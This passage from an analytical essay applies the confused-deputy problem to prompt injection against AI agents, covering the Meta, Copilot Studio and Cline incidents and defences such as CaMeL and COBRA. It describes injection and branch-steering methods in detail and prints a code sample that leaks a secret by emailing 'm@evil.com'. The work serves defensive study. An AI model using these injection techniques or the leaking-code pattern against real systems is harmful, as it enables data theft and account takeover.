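By 2016, the formal work had covered much of task replacement. In the implicit-influence example, the attacker decides what the deputy does without naming anything or passing a reference. The formal definition applies to any program in the language, including one that reads a series of flags from the attacker and performs an action for each. Karp's definition excludes such attacks, but the broader theory covers them and includes a proof that capabilities alone are not enough to stop them.

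However, a programmer wrote both branches of that example. Anyone who reads the code can see that `record` will contain 41 or 42, decide whether the difference matters, and endorse the choice if it doesn't. An assistant's code doesn't list the possible outcomes. An analysis of it would correctly show that the supplier can influence every tool call, but that doesn't help a developer decide which calls to allow.

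The definition also treats all influence alike. An email that changes one word of a reply fails the first condition just as one that extracts the minutes does. The definition ignores probability too, although the same planted text may work on one attempt and fail on the next. A rule against any influence makes sense for a fixed program, where the same input always has the same effect, but it would rule out nearly everything that an assistant that reads mail is meant to do.

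The formal models also do not represent the worker's request separately. The purchase order and the minutes differ in whether the worker would have agreed to send them, but the small language does not represent that difference.

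## Whose authority is misused, and whether acting as the user helps

Hardy's user started the compiler, gave it a file name and damaged the company that owned the compiler. In cases A and B, the supplier never uses the assistant. The office worker starts it, and it uses the office worker's own authority to open the minutes and send them out.

| | Hardy's compiler | Cases A and B |
|---|---|---|
| Who starts the deputy | The attacker | The office worker |
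| What the attacker is entitled to do | Run the compiler and name an output file | Send an email and, in case A, name a document |
| Whose authority does the damage | Tymshare's | The office worker's |
| Who suffers | Tymshare, which owns the deputy | The office worker and the company |

The standard remedy for a confused deputy is to make it act with its invoker's permissions. This suits the first column, where the invoker is the potential attacker, but is much less useful in the second.

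### The invoker's hat

Tymshare's "switch hats" call let the compiler choose which of its two authorities to use for each request. Hardy phrases a request under the user's authority as made "by the authority vested in me by my invoker", and notes that such a request to open BILL would properly fail. The operating system would check the user's rights, and the user had no right to write to BILL. The same check would protect the statistics file from users.

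Hardy disliked the complexity the call added, and it soon proved too limited. Some applications needed more than two authorities, and programs held authority over things other than files. Neither problem had an obvious general solution, and the changes spread through the system. A programmer also had to choose the right authority for each step. This was easy for the compiler, because the step that wrote debugging output always served the user.

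The on-behalf-of token, a credential showing that an agent is acting for a particular user, is today's equivalent of the invoker's hat. A service that receives one can apply the user's permissions instead of the agent's. In *After the identity fix* (2026), a commentary for SC Media, the engineer Nik Kale mentions a framework from the Coalition for Secure AI that uses these tokens to record who delegated what to whom.

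The tokens work well against an invoker who asks for something they aren't allowed to have. When the employee in Siu and colleagues' example asks for everyone's salary, the personnel database checks the employee's permissions and refuses. An attacker who controls the entire task still gains no extra access if the agent is acting with the attacker's own permissions.

In case B, the token changes nothing, because the office worker is allowed to open the minutes and send mail to the supplier. Kale imagines a similar failure, in which a user asks for a summary of a PDF and hidden text gets the agent to change a customer's email address and trigger a password reset. The credentials are all valid, but as Kale says, identity controls establish who is making a request, not whether anyone asked for it. The audit trail doesn't help much either, because it would accurately show that the assistant acted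 for the worker but would not mention the supplier.

Acting as the user limits the damage. If the assistant had run under an account with access to every file in the company, the supplier could have used the email to get the payroll too. With the worker's token, the supplier can reach only what the worker can reach, though that still includes the minutes. Hardy's compiler needed to use its invoker's authority instead of its own, but the assistant in case B needs less authority than its invoker has.

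Kale proposes adding a signed record of what the user asked for. The software around the model would create the record when the request arrives, and each tool would compare the operation it is about to perform with the one named in the record. Like other checks against the user's task, this would stop the leak in case B but not in case A. Kale does not explain how the software would turn plain English into a named operation without a model's help. For high-impact changes, Kale also wants the agent to prepare a draft that a separate tool carries out, after a person approves it if necessary.

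### Meta's account-recovery assistant

A 2026 incident at Meta involved almost the same arrangement of parties as Hardy's story. In March, Meta launched an AI support assistant that could handle account problems from start to finish, including password resets, according to The Next Web's *Hackers asked Meta's AI chatbot to hand over Instagram accounts*. People locked out of Instagram could ask it to email them a reset link. Attackers asked for reset links for other people's accounts and gave their own email addresses. With a link, they could set a new password and log in, unless the account's owner had turned on two-factor authentication.

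Meta's *Incident Notification* (2026), a letter to Nebraska's attorney general, states that the assistant "functioned as intended" and attributes the failure to a bug in separate code, which should have checked that the address matched the one on the account. Hardy had likewise declined to blame the code that wrote the debugging output. The attackers invoked the assistant themselves and gave it a task it was built to perform. The authority they misused was Meta's, since Meta can reset any account's password. Willison (2026), in *Hackers Simply Asked Meta AI to Give Them Access*, remarks that this hardly counts as prompt injection. If Meta's account is right, a plain web form in front of the same code would have had the same flaw.

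Stack Overflow's *AI agents are a confused deputy with the keys to your kingdom* argues that the language model also mattered because a human support worker might have become suspicious when a stranger tried to redirect a celebrity's recovery email. Companies have long relied on that kind of discretion without writing it into software. The article recommends checking that the person in the logged-in session owns the account.

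That remedy is hard to apply to account recovery, because a person who has lost access has no logged-in session. If the assistant had acted only with the permissions of whoever opened the chat, it could not have reset anything, for attackers or for owners. The service has to use its own authority on behalf of someone who can't yet prove who they are. Meta's planned repair leaves that authority in place. Meta says that before relaunching the assistant, it will fix the check that compares the address with the account's existing details. A stranger could then still ask for a reset, but could not have the link sent to a new address.

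Meta disabled the assistant on 31 May, the day it discovered the problem, and cancelled the outstanding links. A spokesperson said the next day that the issue was fixed, but The Next Web, citing TechCrunch, reports that more users said on 2 June that they had lost access. The Maine Attorney General's *Data Breach Notices* (2026) dates the breach from 17 April and lists 20,225 people affected. *Meta confirms thousands of Instagram accounts were hacked*, in the newsletter this week in security, describes that figure as a minimum. In its letter, Meta calls its count of 37 for Nebraska an upper bound, because the real owners may have made some of the resets.

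### A form that gave orders to a company's agent

Companies use Microsoft's Copilot Studio to build agents that work with their own data. Some of these agents process forms submitted through SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing system. According to CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026), the firm Capsule Security found that text entered in such a form could override the agent's instructions and make it send company data to an attacker's server.

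The company that built the agent had set its task, and the attacker used the form to supply a different one. The agent used the company's authority over its own data. It is less clear who counts as the invoker. STAR Labs' *CVE-2026-21520* (2026) reports Microsoft's ratings for the flaw, under which an attacker needs no privileges and no user has to do anything. This suggests that the arrival of the form was enough to start the agent. If so, the attacker started the run, as at Meta. But unlike Meta's attackers, the person filling in the form was entitled only to provide information for someone else's task.

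An on-behalf-of token for the employee who built the agent would not have stopped the leak, since that employee presumably had access to the data. Running the agent with the permissions of the person who filled in the form would have prevented the leak, but it would also have blocked any legitimate processing that needed the company's records.

Microsoft's repair was narrower. Claw Times (2026) dates the patch to 15 January 2026, about seven weeks after Capsule reported the flaw. According to Kale, the patch closed one path by which data could leave but did not fix the underlying problem. Claw Times reports that data could still get out. Capsule found a similar flaw in Salesforce's Agentforce, and Salesforce responded by requiring human confirmation by default when an agent acts through email. The person confirming may know whether anyone wanted the action.

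### The GitHub issue and Cline's triage bot

Cline is an open-source coding assistant. Its maintainers take bug reports on GitHub, where anyone with an account can open an "issue". In December 2025 they added a bot, running on Anthropic's Claude, to read and sort new issues. Opening an issue started the bot and put the issue's title in its prompt, so a stranger could both start the bot and give it instructions. In *Clinejection*, Adnan Khan (2026) describes finding this flaw and testing it on a copy of Cline's repository, where Claude followed the planted instructions in every attempt.

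Khan writes that the bot had broad privileges, while Cline's *Postmortem* (2026) describes its permissions as limited. Both are right, because they refer to different kinds of access. On GitHub, the bot could only read the code and edit issues, which is close to what an ordinary visitor can do. But it could also run commands on the machine it ran on, and it shared a store of saved files with the job that published Cline's nightly releases. An attacker could use those files to get code into that job, which held the credentials for publishing Cline's software.

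Cline had therefore partly made the bot act as its invoker, but it was still exposed because programs have authority through more than one mechanism, which is a reason Hardy gave for abandoning the "switch hats" call. GitHub's permissions covered what the bot did on GitHub but not what it could do through shared files. The release job was also a deputy in the older sense. It performed its usual task with material from a less trusted source, so it could use its publishing rights for someone who had none.

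Khan reported the flaw on 1 January 2026 and, after several unanswered messages, published it on 9 February. Cline removed the bot within half an hour and began replacing its credentials, but deleted the wrong token for npm, the registry that distributes its command-line tool. On 17 February someone used the surviving token to release a version of the tool that was unchanged except that it also installed OpenClaw, an unrelated AI agent. The release stayed up for about eight hours, and LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026) quotes a figure of about 4,000 downloads.

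The account that LWN quotes states as fact that the attacker got the token by planting instructions in an issue title. Khan is less certain. Someone appears to have tampered with Cline's release jobs in late January and early February, but Khan says it is unclear whether they got in through the bot, though that was the most obvious route. The bot could certainly be hijacked, but it is only likely that a hijacking led to the release.

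Cline's repairs mostly concerned what the bot could reach. Besides removing the bot, Cline stopped release jobs that handle credentials from using the shared files. It also changed its publishing system to support OpenID Connect, as The Hacker News (2026) reports. Under that standard, a release job can prove its identity each time it publishes instead of keeping a long-lived token, so there would be no old token for someone to use a week later. But hostile code inside the release job would still have the job's identity, and only the separation from the shared files guards against that. Khan had suggested keeping the bot but removing its ability to run commands and write files.

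### Starting a run and setting its task

| | Meta | Copilot Studio | Cline |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who started the run | The attacker | Apparently the attacker | The attacker |
| Who supplied the task | The attacker, from the services on offer | The attacker, in place of the company's task | The attacker, in place of the maintainers' task |
| Whose authority the agent used | Meta's | The company's | Cline's |
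| What the repair changed | Withdrew the assistant, with an address check to follow | Closed one way for data to leave | Removed the bot, separated the release jobs and replaced credentials |
| Would acting as the person who started the run have helped? | Yes, but real owners could not have recovered accounts either | Yes, if the agent's normal work needed no company data | Only if the limits covered the machine as well as GitHub |

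None of these incidents has quite the same parties as case B, in which an innocent user starts the agent. The 2025 email attack on ChatGPT that OpenAI described comes closer, because the planted text reached an assistant working for the email's recipient. The Copilot Studio and Cline attacks resemble case B in that the attacker replaced a task someone else had set.

The person who ran the compiler was also entitled to say what it should do. When an agent responds automatically to forms or bug reports, the company decides in advance what the agent is for, but a stranger's message starts it. "Act as the invoker" could then mean using the company's permissions, which is dangerous, or the stranger's, which is safe but may leave the agent unable to do its job.

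In Hardy's story the invoker was the attacker, so acting as the invoker also meant having no more authority than the attacker. In case B, only that limit on authority protects the minutes. The limit amounts to the rule about dropping privileges that David C passes on, and it has the same drawback in case A.

### How common each pattern is

These incidents can't show how often attackers invoke an agent themselves and how often they reach it through an innocent user. They also differ in kind. Attackers used the flaw at Meta for about six weeks. The Cline case involved one unauthorised release whose origin is still uncertain. STAR Labs lists the Copilot Studio flaw as not exploited, so it may never have harmed anyone outside a researcher's test.

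Counting entries in public catalogues would not settle the matter either. MITRE's *CVE-2026-21520* (2026), the official record of the Copilot Studio flaw, files it under general command injection, a classification that Microsoft supplied. Kale treats the flaw as an example of both the confused deputy and prompt injection, but a search for MITRE's numbers for those two categories would miss it.

The reports probably also under-represent cases where acting as the user does not help, because those cases are harder to notice. Thousands of Instagram users had reason to notice that they could no longer log in, and anyone could compare Cline's unexpected release with its published code. The office worker in case B sees no such sign of the leak.

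## What remains of the attack when the task is fixed in advance

Having the assistant act as the office worker doesn't protect the minutes in case B. A developer could instead fix the assistant's steps before it reads any of the supplier's email. If this works, the attacker can no longer replace the task and can only supply values to a program with fixed steps, which is roughly the position Hardy's user was in.

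*Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (2025) states the general principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, that input must not be able to trigger any action with harmful side effects. The paper considers it unlikely that general-purpose agents can offer reliable guarantees with the current kind of language model, so its designs restrict what an agent can do. How much the principle forbids depends on what counts as triggering an action. In case B, the hidden passage triggers the message to the supplier, whereas in case A the worker's request triggers it and the email only determines what the assistant attaches.

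### A planner that never reads the email

In 2023 Willison proposed dividing an agent's work between two language models. A planner reads the user's request and decides which tools to use, but never reads outside content. A quarantined model, which has no tools, reads that content and returns answers. Planted instructions can still mislead the quarantined model, but only into returning a bad answer.

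CaMeL, which Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, is the best-known system of this kind. Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, and Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, both build on it and describe how it handles a request:

1. *The program.* The planner receives the user's request and descriptions of the tools, and writes a Python program to carry out the request. It does this before the system fetches anything from outside.
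2. *The interpreter.* Ordinary software runs the program and makes the tool calls. It stores each result in a variable, which the planner can refer to by name but cannot read.
3. *The quarantined model.* When the program needs something from a text, such as a summary or a date, it passes the text to the quarantined model and stores the answer in another variable.
4. *The labels.* The interpreter keeps a record, for each value, of where it came from and who may read it. It carries these records over to any new value it computes from old ones.
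5. *The policy check.* Before a tool call runs, a function that the developer has written examines the arguments and their labels, and allows or refuses the call. One such policy might refuse to email private data to anyone who isn't allowed to read it.

The first three steps provide control-flow integrity, which means that outside content cannot add a step to the plan. The last two are a separate protection that covers the values passing through the planned steps. Several of the published tests were run with the policies switched off.

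### The two emails under CaMeL

When the worker asks for a summary of the supplier's email, the planner might write:

```
email = read_email("latest from supplier")
summary = quarantined_model("Summarise this email", email)
show(summary)
```

The hidden passage in case B reaches only the quarantined model. The program has no line that opens another file or sends mail, so the attack fails however persuasive the passage is. A check on tool calls needs a record of the user's task, and the program provides one. A different model writes the program, and it has read nothing from the supplier.

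The supplier can still influence the summary. If the quarantined model follows the hidden passage, it could report that the supplier's bank details have changed, and the worker might act on that. CaMeL's original evaluation on AgentDojo includes a mild example. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that one of the two successful injections worked because the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the benchmark's text matching counted the quotation as a success for the attacker. The paper treats this as a quirk of the scoring, but the case still shows planted words reaching the user through an ordinary answer.

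For case A, the program has to be longer:

```
email = read_email("latest from supplier")
name = quarantined_model("Which file does the sender want?", email)
document = open_file(name)
send_email(to=supplier, attachment=document)
```

This program already contains every step the supplier needs. The quarantined model can cause the leak by doing its job correctly and returning the file name of the board minutes. Only the policy check before the last line can prevent this. Like the other checks, it can distinguish the minutes from a purchase order only if someone has recorded which documents the supplier may read. Foerster and colleagues note that writing such policies takes expertise, that no automatic method exists for deriving them, and that users differ in what they are willing to share.

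CaMeL therefore removes the attack in case B but leaves the one in case A largely unchanged. Garby and colleagues counted both cases in AgentDojo's banking tasks, which pair 16 user requests with nine attacks. In 97 of the 144 pairs, the attack needs a tool call or a file that the plan for the user's request would never include, as in case B. In the other 47, the planned steps could be enough for the attack, as in case A. The fixed plan alone should therefore stop the attack in about two thirds of the pairs, although that proportion depends on which attacks the benchmark's designers chose to write.

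The remaining third rarely succeeded either. With its policies off, CaMeL resisted the attack in all 141 of these runs on GPT-5.2 and in 138 of 141 on a second model, MiMo-v2.5. This is weak evidence about case A, because AgentDojo's standard attacks are instructions addressed to the assistant, whereas the supplier in case A only has to give a plausible answer to a question the program was always going to ask.

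### Miller's doubts about the labels

CaMeL stands for "capabilities for machine learning", and its developers call the labels on values "capabilities". Mark Miller objected to the word in May 2025, in a mailing-list thread that Karp had started, *Capabilities and prompt injection* (Karp, 2025). Going by a short description of the system, he wrote that these labels "don't even sound vaguely like ocaps", his term for capabilities in Hardy's sense. He thought they sounded like taint tracking, in which software marks data from an untrusted source and follows the mark through a program.

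Miller called this a "brief cursory reaction" and said he was not criticising the paper. He thought taint tracking was probably a good defence against a model that unintentionally writes exploitable code. But he denied that it gave the hard guarantees CaMeL's developers claimed, because a fallible programmer might occasionally write any code that a malicious one would. A real guarantee would require full information-flow control, which would also reject much correct code unless the model had learned to write programs that pass the check.

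A CaMeL label describes a value that the program already has, and a separate policy decides what may happen to that value. A capability would prevent the supplier in case A from designating the minutes by name alone, but the label does not.

His objection to the guarantees applies to the policy checks, and Garby and colleagues later found flaws there of the kind he expected. They also note that CaMeL has no proof of soundness and that its developers list a formal treatment as future work. The objection does not apply to the protection in case B, which does not rely on labels because the planner never reads the email.

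CaMeL does go further than simple taint tracking. If a program sends an email only when an account balance is above some threshold, the interpreter registers that the decision depended on a secret and refuses the call. But Garby and colleagues show that a roundabout version gets through. It works like this:

```
tmp = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
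```

When the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and the program skips the assignment to `rich`. The interpreter updates a variable's label only when an assignment runs, so `rich` still counts as public. The email goes out and reveals that the balance is high.

A second leak lies outside the interpreter. When a program fails, CaMeL has the planner try again in an ordinary loop with no labels. A secret can affect whether a policy blocks an attempt, so someone able to repeat the process could recover the secret one bit at a time.

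An attacker who plants an email can't insert the five-line program above, because the planner writes the code from the user's request. The planner would have to produce it by accident, which is the remote possibility Miller had in mind. Garby and colleagues mention another flaw that seems more likely to matter in practice. Putting an untrusted value inside a text template makes the result count as trusted, and planners use templates all the time. In case A, a planner that built a folder path around the supplier's file name could lose the record that the supplier had chosen the file.

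Miller's prediction about the drawbacks of full tracking has held up less well so far. Garby and colleagues built an agent called Randori in a language of their own, and used Lean to prove that secrets cannot affect public results except through whether the program finishes. With GPT-5.2, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs of the banking tasks, against 32 for CaMeL with its policies off. However, Randori's planner can endorse outside data in advance where the user's request seems to need it. Without endorsement, completed runs fell from 36 to 30 on Qwen3.7-plus and from 31 to 26 on MiMo-v2.5.

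Endorsement also allowed the only successful attacks, in two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to make a payment described in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a different payment request.

### When one agent's data is another agent's request

Many systems now have a main agent that hands parts of a job to specialised agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that task replacement can return in such a system even when every agent runs CaMeL.

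In one demonstration, a user asks for a Slack message to a colleague summarising job applicants. One agent reads the applicant database, where an attacker has planted an instruction to email the data to an outside address. The main agent has the quarantined model summarise the result, then asks a notification agent to send the summary, which it includes in the request. The notification agent treats the main agent as its user, so its planner reads the planted instruction as part of a trusted request and writes a program that sends both the Slack message and the email.

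The main agent and the database agent followed their original plans. Peters-Gill and colleagues prove that the problem is general in systems where agents call each other as tools. If any tool returns untrusted data and the agents are flexible enough to pass results on, some user request will let that data influence another agent's plan.

Their repair, multi-CaMeL, splits each call between agents into instructions, which may not depend on any tool's output, and data, which the receiving planner can refer to but not read. They tested it on a version of AgentDojo they had divided among several agents, with 949 attacks on each of five models. When each agent ran CaMeL separately, 0.5 percent of attacks succeeded on GPT-4.1, 0.4 percent on Gemini 2.5 Pro and none on the other three models. Every successful attack worked in the way just described, and multi-CaMeL stopped them all.

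### The cost in completed tasks

In its first AgentDojo results, in 2025, CaMeL was much more secure than marking off untrusted text or repeating the user's request, and Peters-Gill and colleagues describe the reduction in completed tasks as comparatively modest. Later comparisons were less favourable on task completion. *AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) tested ten defences on five models against an attacker that kept rewriting its text according to what had worked. CaMeL was the most effective defence overall, but it also reduced task completion the most on four of the five models.

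The table gives the share of tasks that agents completed when nobody was attacking them.

| Test | Model | No CaMeL | CaMeL without policies | With a further protection |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Multi-agent AgentDojo (Peters-Gill and colleagues) | GPT-5.5 | 86.6% | 73.2% | 66.0% (multi-CaMeL) |
| The same, on the 45 tasks the model did not refuse | Claude Fable 5 | 91.1% | 84.4% | 84.4% (multi-CaMeL) |
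| The same, on all 97 tasks | GPT-4.1 | 78.4% | 38.1% | 24.7% (multi-CaMeL) |
| AgentDojo banking (Garby and colleagues) | GPT-5.2 | Not given | 66.7% | 37.5% (CaMeL's policies) |

Stronger models lose less performance under CaMeL, presumably because they are better at writing a whole program without seeing any data, but they may also gain less security. GPT-5.5 resisted all 949 attacks without any CaMeL protection, so for that model the benchmark shows a loss of performance and no gain in security. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution against reading this as immunity, since participants in a large public competition successfully attacked every frontier model tested.

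With the policies on, CaMeL completed 18 of 48 banking runs, down from 32, although the margin of error is wide because there were only 16 distinct tasks. In return, every attack failed in the runs that finished. TypeGuard, which enforces similar policies, completed 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks with them off and 8 with them on. Its developers say many of these tasks involve data flows "that no secure policy would admit".

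Most of the failures that Peters-Gill and colleagues examined happened because the need for another step became clear only after a tool returned its result. An ordinary agent can add the step, but a CaMeL agent can only follow the branches in its program. In some cases, an agent could not find data for the requested machine or dates and returned data for similar ones instead, and the main agent's program continued without detecting the substitution.

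A completed task may also hide a loss of quality. One request was to visit two people's websites and send them feedback. Under multi-CaMeL, the planner, an older Gemini model, wrote the feedback into its program in advance. It complimented one owner on a "clean design" without having seen it. Peters-Gill and colleagues present this run as blocking the attack and completing the task.

### Choosing among the branches of a plan

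A plan can include alternatives, and outside content can determine which one the program follows. Suppose the worker asks the assistant to send the supplier the signed contract if the supplier has confirmed the price, and to file the email otherwise. The supplier can get the contract just by writing that the price is confirmed. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. It leaves control-flow integrity intact, because every step comes from the original plan. The attack has the same form as Rajani and colleagues' implicit-influence example.

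Branch steering matters most for computer-use agents, which operate ordinary programs by looking at the screen and clicking. A planner that can't see the screen has to prepare for pop-ups, failed clicks and unfamiliar layouts. The plans Foerster and colleagues generated for these agents averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with 5 and 4 for CaMeL's plans on AgentDojo. About half of each plan was fallbacks that did not run.

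The researchers used one of those fallbacks to build an attack. Nearly every plan for a browser includes a step to find and dismiss a cookie notice, so they placed a fake notice inside an advertisement. The screen-reading model reported it as real, and the agent clicked through to a site the attacker had chosen. Comparing the screen with the page's underlying structure caught some versions but not others. A second model acting as a checker had trouble rejecting fake notices without also rejecting legitimate steps.

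Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, have the planner limit which sites and tools each branch may use, and which values it may send, before the agent sees anything. Their system, COBRA, enforces these limits with ordinary code that inspects outgoing web requests and tool calls, because the effect of a click can't be determined from the click alone. On their benchmark of 101 tasks, attacks succeeded 94.4 percent of the time against an ordinary agent, 89.5 percent against one that only fixed its plan in advance, and never against COBRA. COBRA wrongly blocked 4 of 138 harmless runs.

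The benchmark counts an attack as successful when a harmful action breaks the limits in force at that point. The zero result therefore shows that COBRA enforces its limits, but it is weaker evidence that a planner will always choose the right limits.

Tests on WASP, an outside benchmark, show that the limits need to cover operations as well as websites. In one WASP task, the user asks for a comment on a software project, and the attacker tries to add an access key to a project on the same website. When COBRA could restrict only which websites the agent contacted, all 14 attacks that stayed on the permitted site succeeded. With an approved list of each site's operations, it blocked all 14, along with the five that crossed to another site. Two further attacks changed only the wording of a comment the agent was allowed to post, and COBRA does not check wording.

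Planning without seeing the screen also reduces performance. Foerster and colleagues preserved at most 57 percent of a frontier model's performance, and only by allowing five attempts at each task. Zingrillo and colleagues also allowed up to five attempts at each of 361 tasks. Claude Sonnet 5 completed 51.0 percent of them as an ordinary agent and 38.8 percent when it filled both roles in COBRA. A small screen-reading model completed 23.5 percent alone and 36.8 percent in COBRA, but there it had GPT-5 as its planner.

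### Requests that leave the task to the email

Suppose the worker writes "do what this email asks". The planner has to list the steps without reading the email, but those steps appear only in the email. Foerster and colleagues call this a fundamental limitation of separating planning from untrusted data.

Ma and colleagues sort requests by how much they leave to outside content:

- *Fully specified.* The user states the action and its details, as in a request to change an address to a particular street and number.
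- *Parameters open.* The user states the action, but the agent must find a detail elsewhere. Their example is paying the bill in a named file, and case A is of this kind.
- *Action open.* The user leaves the action itself to the content, as in a request to do everything on a to-do list at some web address.

On an undefended GPT-4o-mini agent, AgentDojo's standard attack succeeded on 87.5 percent of open-action requests, compared with 63.9 and 43.3 percent for the other two kinds. Filters that look for suspicious text do badly on open-action requests because an attacker can write the planted task as one more entry on the list. PIGuard, one such filter, blocked the standard attack entirely on this model, but it let through 54.2 percent of adapted attacks on open-action requests and 17.3 percent of those on fully specified ones.

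Progent and DRIFT, which both limit tool calls, kept the attack success rate at 11 percent or less on every kind of request. For many open-action requests, they did so by permitting only read-only tools. An assistant limited to those tools could tell the worker what the email asks for but could not carry out the request.

A planner can also try to cover every possible instruction. In one banking task, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL's planner sometimes responded with a program that read each instruction in the file and had a branch for every tool. The planner had written every branch in advance, so the file added no step to the plan. But whoever wrote the file could choose any tool, which amounts to replacing the task. With the policies off, two attacks succeeded that a narrower plan would have made impossible.

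It is also unclear what would count as an attack on such a request. If the worker writes "do what this email asks" and the email openly asks for the board minutes, an assistant that sends them has done what the worker said. The payment file that defeated Randori raises the same difficulty, because the user had asked the agent to pay whatever the file specified. The other successful injection in CaMeL's 2025 evaluation was also a payment that followed a document's instructions, and CaMeL's developers excluded such cases from the threats they meant to address.

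Asking the worker again would help. The quarantined model could list the requests in the email, and the assistant could show the worker this list and plan only the items the worker approves. Each approved item then becomes a request from the worker, so the planner can write a program for it as usual. But the worker has to read the list carefully, and an item such as "send the document the supplier mentioned" would bring back case A.

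## Experiments on replacing the task and on staying close to it

Fixing an assistant's steps in advance stops an attacker from replacing its task. How much protection this gives depends partly on whether attacks succeed because they replace the task. A planted goal can use any tool the assistant has, but a goal far from the user's request is also easy to notice. In two sets of experiments from late 2026, models resisted such goals better than they resisted small changes to the work they were already doing.

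### Small changes and unrelated goals

In one of AgentDojo's banking tasks, the user asks for a recurring payment to a specified account, for the amount they usually pay for Spotify. The correct tool call schedules a payment of 50.0 for 1 April. An attacker could plant an instruction to change the user's password, which is unrelated to the request, or to schedule the same payment with the amount changed to 51.0.

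Gong, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *On Task, Off Track*, compared these two sorts of instruction on seven models, including GPT-5.6 Sol, Claude Opus 5 and Meta-SecAlign-70B, whose developers trained it to resist injection. The tests used 1,399 document tasks, such as answering questions and completing code, and agent tasks from AgentDojo and a newer collection called AgentDyn. For each task there were three sets of planted instructions:

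- *Unrelated goals*, which came from existing benchmarks, such as changing the password.
- *Close but wrong results*, such as scheduling the payment for 2 April.
- *Close but harmful results*, such as raising the payment to 51.0.

Each model received three instructions of each sort, and an attack counted as successful if any of the three worked. The table shows the range across the seven models.

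| Tasks | Unrelated goal | Close but wrong | Close but harmful |
|---|---|---|---|
| Documents | 0.3–15.5% | 9.6–51.3% | 4.1–32.8% |
| AgentDojo | 1.5–5.9% | 7.5–32.4% | 2.8–12.8% |
| AgentDyn | 0.0–6.3% | 16.5–43.4% | 4.0–21.1% |

Attacks that stayed close to the task, whether they aimed for a wrong result or a harmful one, succeeded more often than attacks with unrelated goals for every model in all three settings. Meta-SecAlign's resistance to conspicuous instructions evidently did not carry over to plausible ones. On the document tasks, the attack success rate against it was 3.2 percent for unrelated goals, 36.7 percent for wrong results and 18.4 percent for harmful ones.

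The gap is much smaller for harmful results, which matter more to an attacker. A payment sent a day late is a mistake, but few attackers would plant an instruction to cause it. On AgentDojo, Claude Opus 5's rate was 1.5 percent for unrelated goals and 2.8 percent for harmful results.

The two sets of attacks also differ in more than how close they stay to the user's task. Gong and colleagues point out that the attacker's goal is different in each set, so their results don't show that staying close would help an attacker who already has a particular goal. For agents, the test of success differed too. A close attack aimed at a tool call only had to produce the right call with the right main arguments, whereas an unrelated attack had to pass AgentDojo's own check, which inspects the state of the simulated accounts afterwards. All the instructions were bare sentences with no added persuasion,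 which probably hurts an odd request more than a plausible one.

The model that wrote the close attacks knew the user's request and a correct answer to it, which the supplier would not know. This knowledge doesn't always help. *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (Hofer, Debenedetti and Tramèr, 2026) found that attacks optimised to work across many user tasks did at least as well as those optimised for one known task.

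### Three meanings of "close"

A close attack in this benchmark can go beyond argument control by adding a new action. In one AgentDyn task, the user asks the agent to star any of their code repositories that have no stars yet. One of the "close but harmful" instructions tells the agent to delete the repository first. This instruction concerns the right repository, but the user never asked the agent to delete anything.

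Chang, Nikolić and colleagues (2026), in *The Devil is in the Context*, separate several things that "close" can mean. They classify injection attacks along nine dimensions, three of which compare the attack with the user's task:

- *Topic.* The user asks for a summary of an invoice. A planted instruction to insert an advertisement is off-topic, and one to report a lower total is on-topic.
- *Choice of tool or change of content.* An instruction to pay the invoice adds an action. An instruction to report a total of $50 instead of $500 changes only what the summary contains.
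- *Completion of the task.* The user asks the agent to send a report to their supervisor. An instruction to send it only to the attacker disrupts the task, while an instruction to send it to both preserves it.

Case B is off-topic and adds actions, but it preserves the task because the worker still gets a summary. Case A is on-topic and changes only content. Whether it preserves the task is debatable, since the worker asked the assistant to send whatever the supplier requested.

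Real attacks combine these properties in other ways. In an attack on GitHub users, someone planted instructions in a public bug report. An agent asked to deal with the report then copied information from private repositories into a public one. Chang and colleagues classify this attack as on-topic and task-preserving, although it added actions. In another attack, a visible instruction in a spreadsheet cell made a command-line assistant put customer data into a special character sequence in its answer. The Mac's Terminal program interpreted the sequence and sent the data out in a network request. The model chose no tool, so this attack leaked data by changing only the content of the answer.

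The labels describe what the attacker intended, so they can't show which attacks work best. Chang and colleagues ran one small test of effects, pairing each of 40 user tasks from AgentDojo's office suite with a randomly chosen attack. They had a model rewrite each case so that the attack was on-topic, changed only content, and took effect only under a stated condition. None of the 40 original attacks succeeded against GPT-5.6-Luna, but 7 of the 40 rewritten ones did (17.5 percent). One succeeded against CaMeL, which fixes the plan but not the content of its steps.

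This agrees with the results of Gong and colleagues, but it can't show which of the three changes produced the result. The rewriting could also alter the user's task and the attacker's goal. The condition alone may explain why the MELON defence did not help. MELON checks how an agent behaves when the user's task is hidden from it, and an instruction that depends on a particular user request stays inactive during that check.

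### The same goal from different apparent speakers

The experiment in which Ye and colleagues related leaks to a model's confusion of roles held the attacker's goal constant. The user always wanted a short summary of a Wikipedia page, and the planted command always told the agent to find a file of secrets and upload it. Every attempt was therefore an attempt at task replacement. What varied was the text around the command, for which there were 212 templates:

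- 73 stated in plain words where the command came from, for example that the following text was from the user.
- 42 copied the headers that other models use to mark a speaker's turn.
- 67 were slight variations on such headers.
- 30 gave no sign of a speaker and surrounded the command with things like filler Latin.

All 1,000 attempts used one small model, gpt-oss-20b, and ten web pages. For each attempt, the researchers measured "Userness", the probability that the command was user text, as estimated by a classifier from the model's internal activity. Only 24 percent of the templates named the user as the speaker, but they accounted for all of the top 5 percent by Userness.

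Since the command never changed, the difference between 2 percent success at the lowest Userness and 70 percent at the highest cannot be due to the goal. Ye and colleagues also checked whether Userness merely reflected which speaker the template named. They fitted this model:

log-odds of success = −2.16 + 6.01 × Userness + 0.84 (if the template names the user) − 0.64 (if it names a tool)

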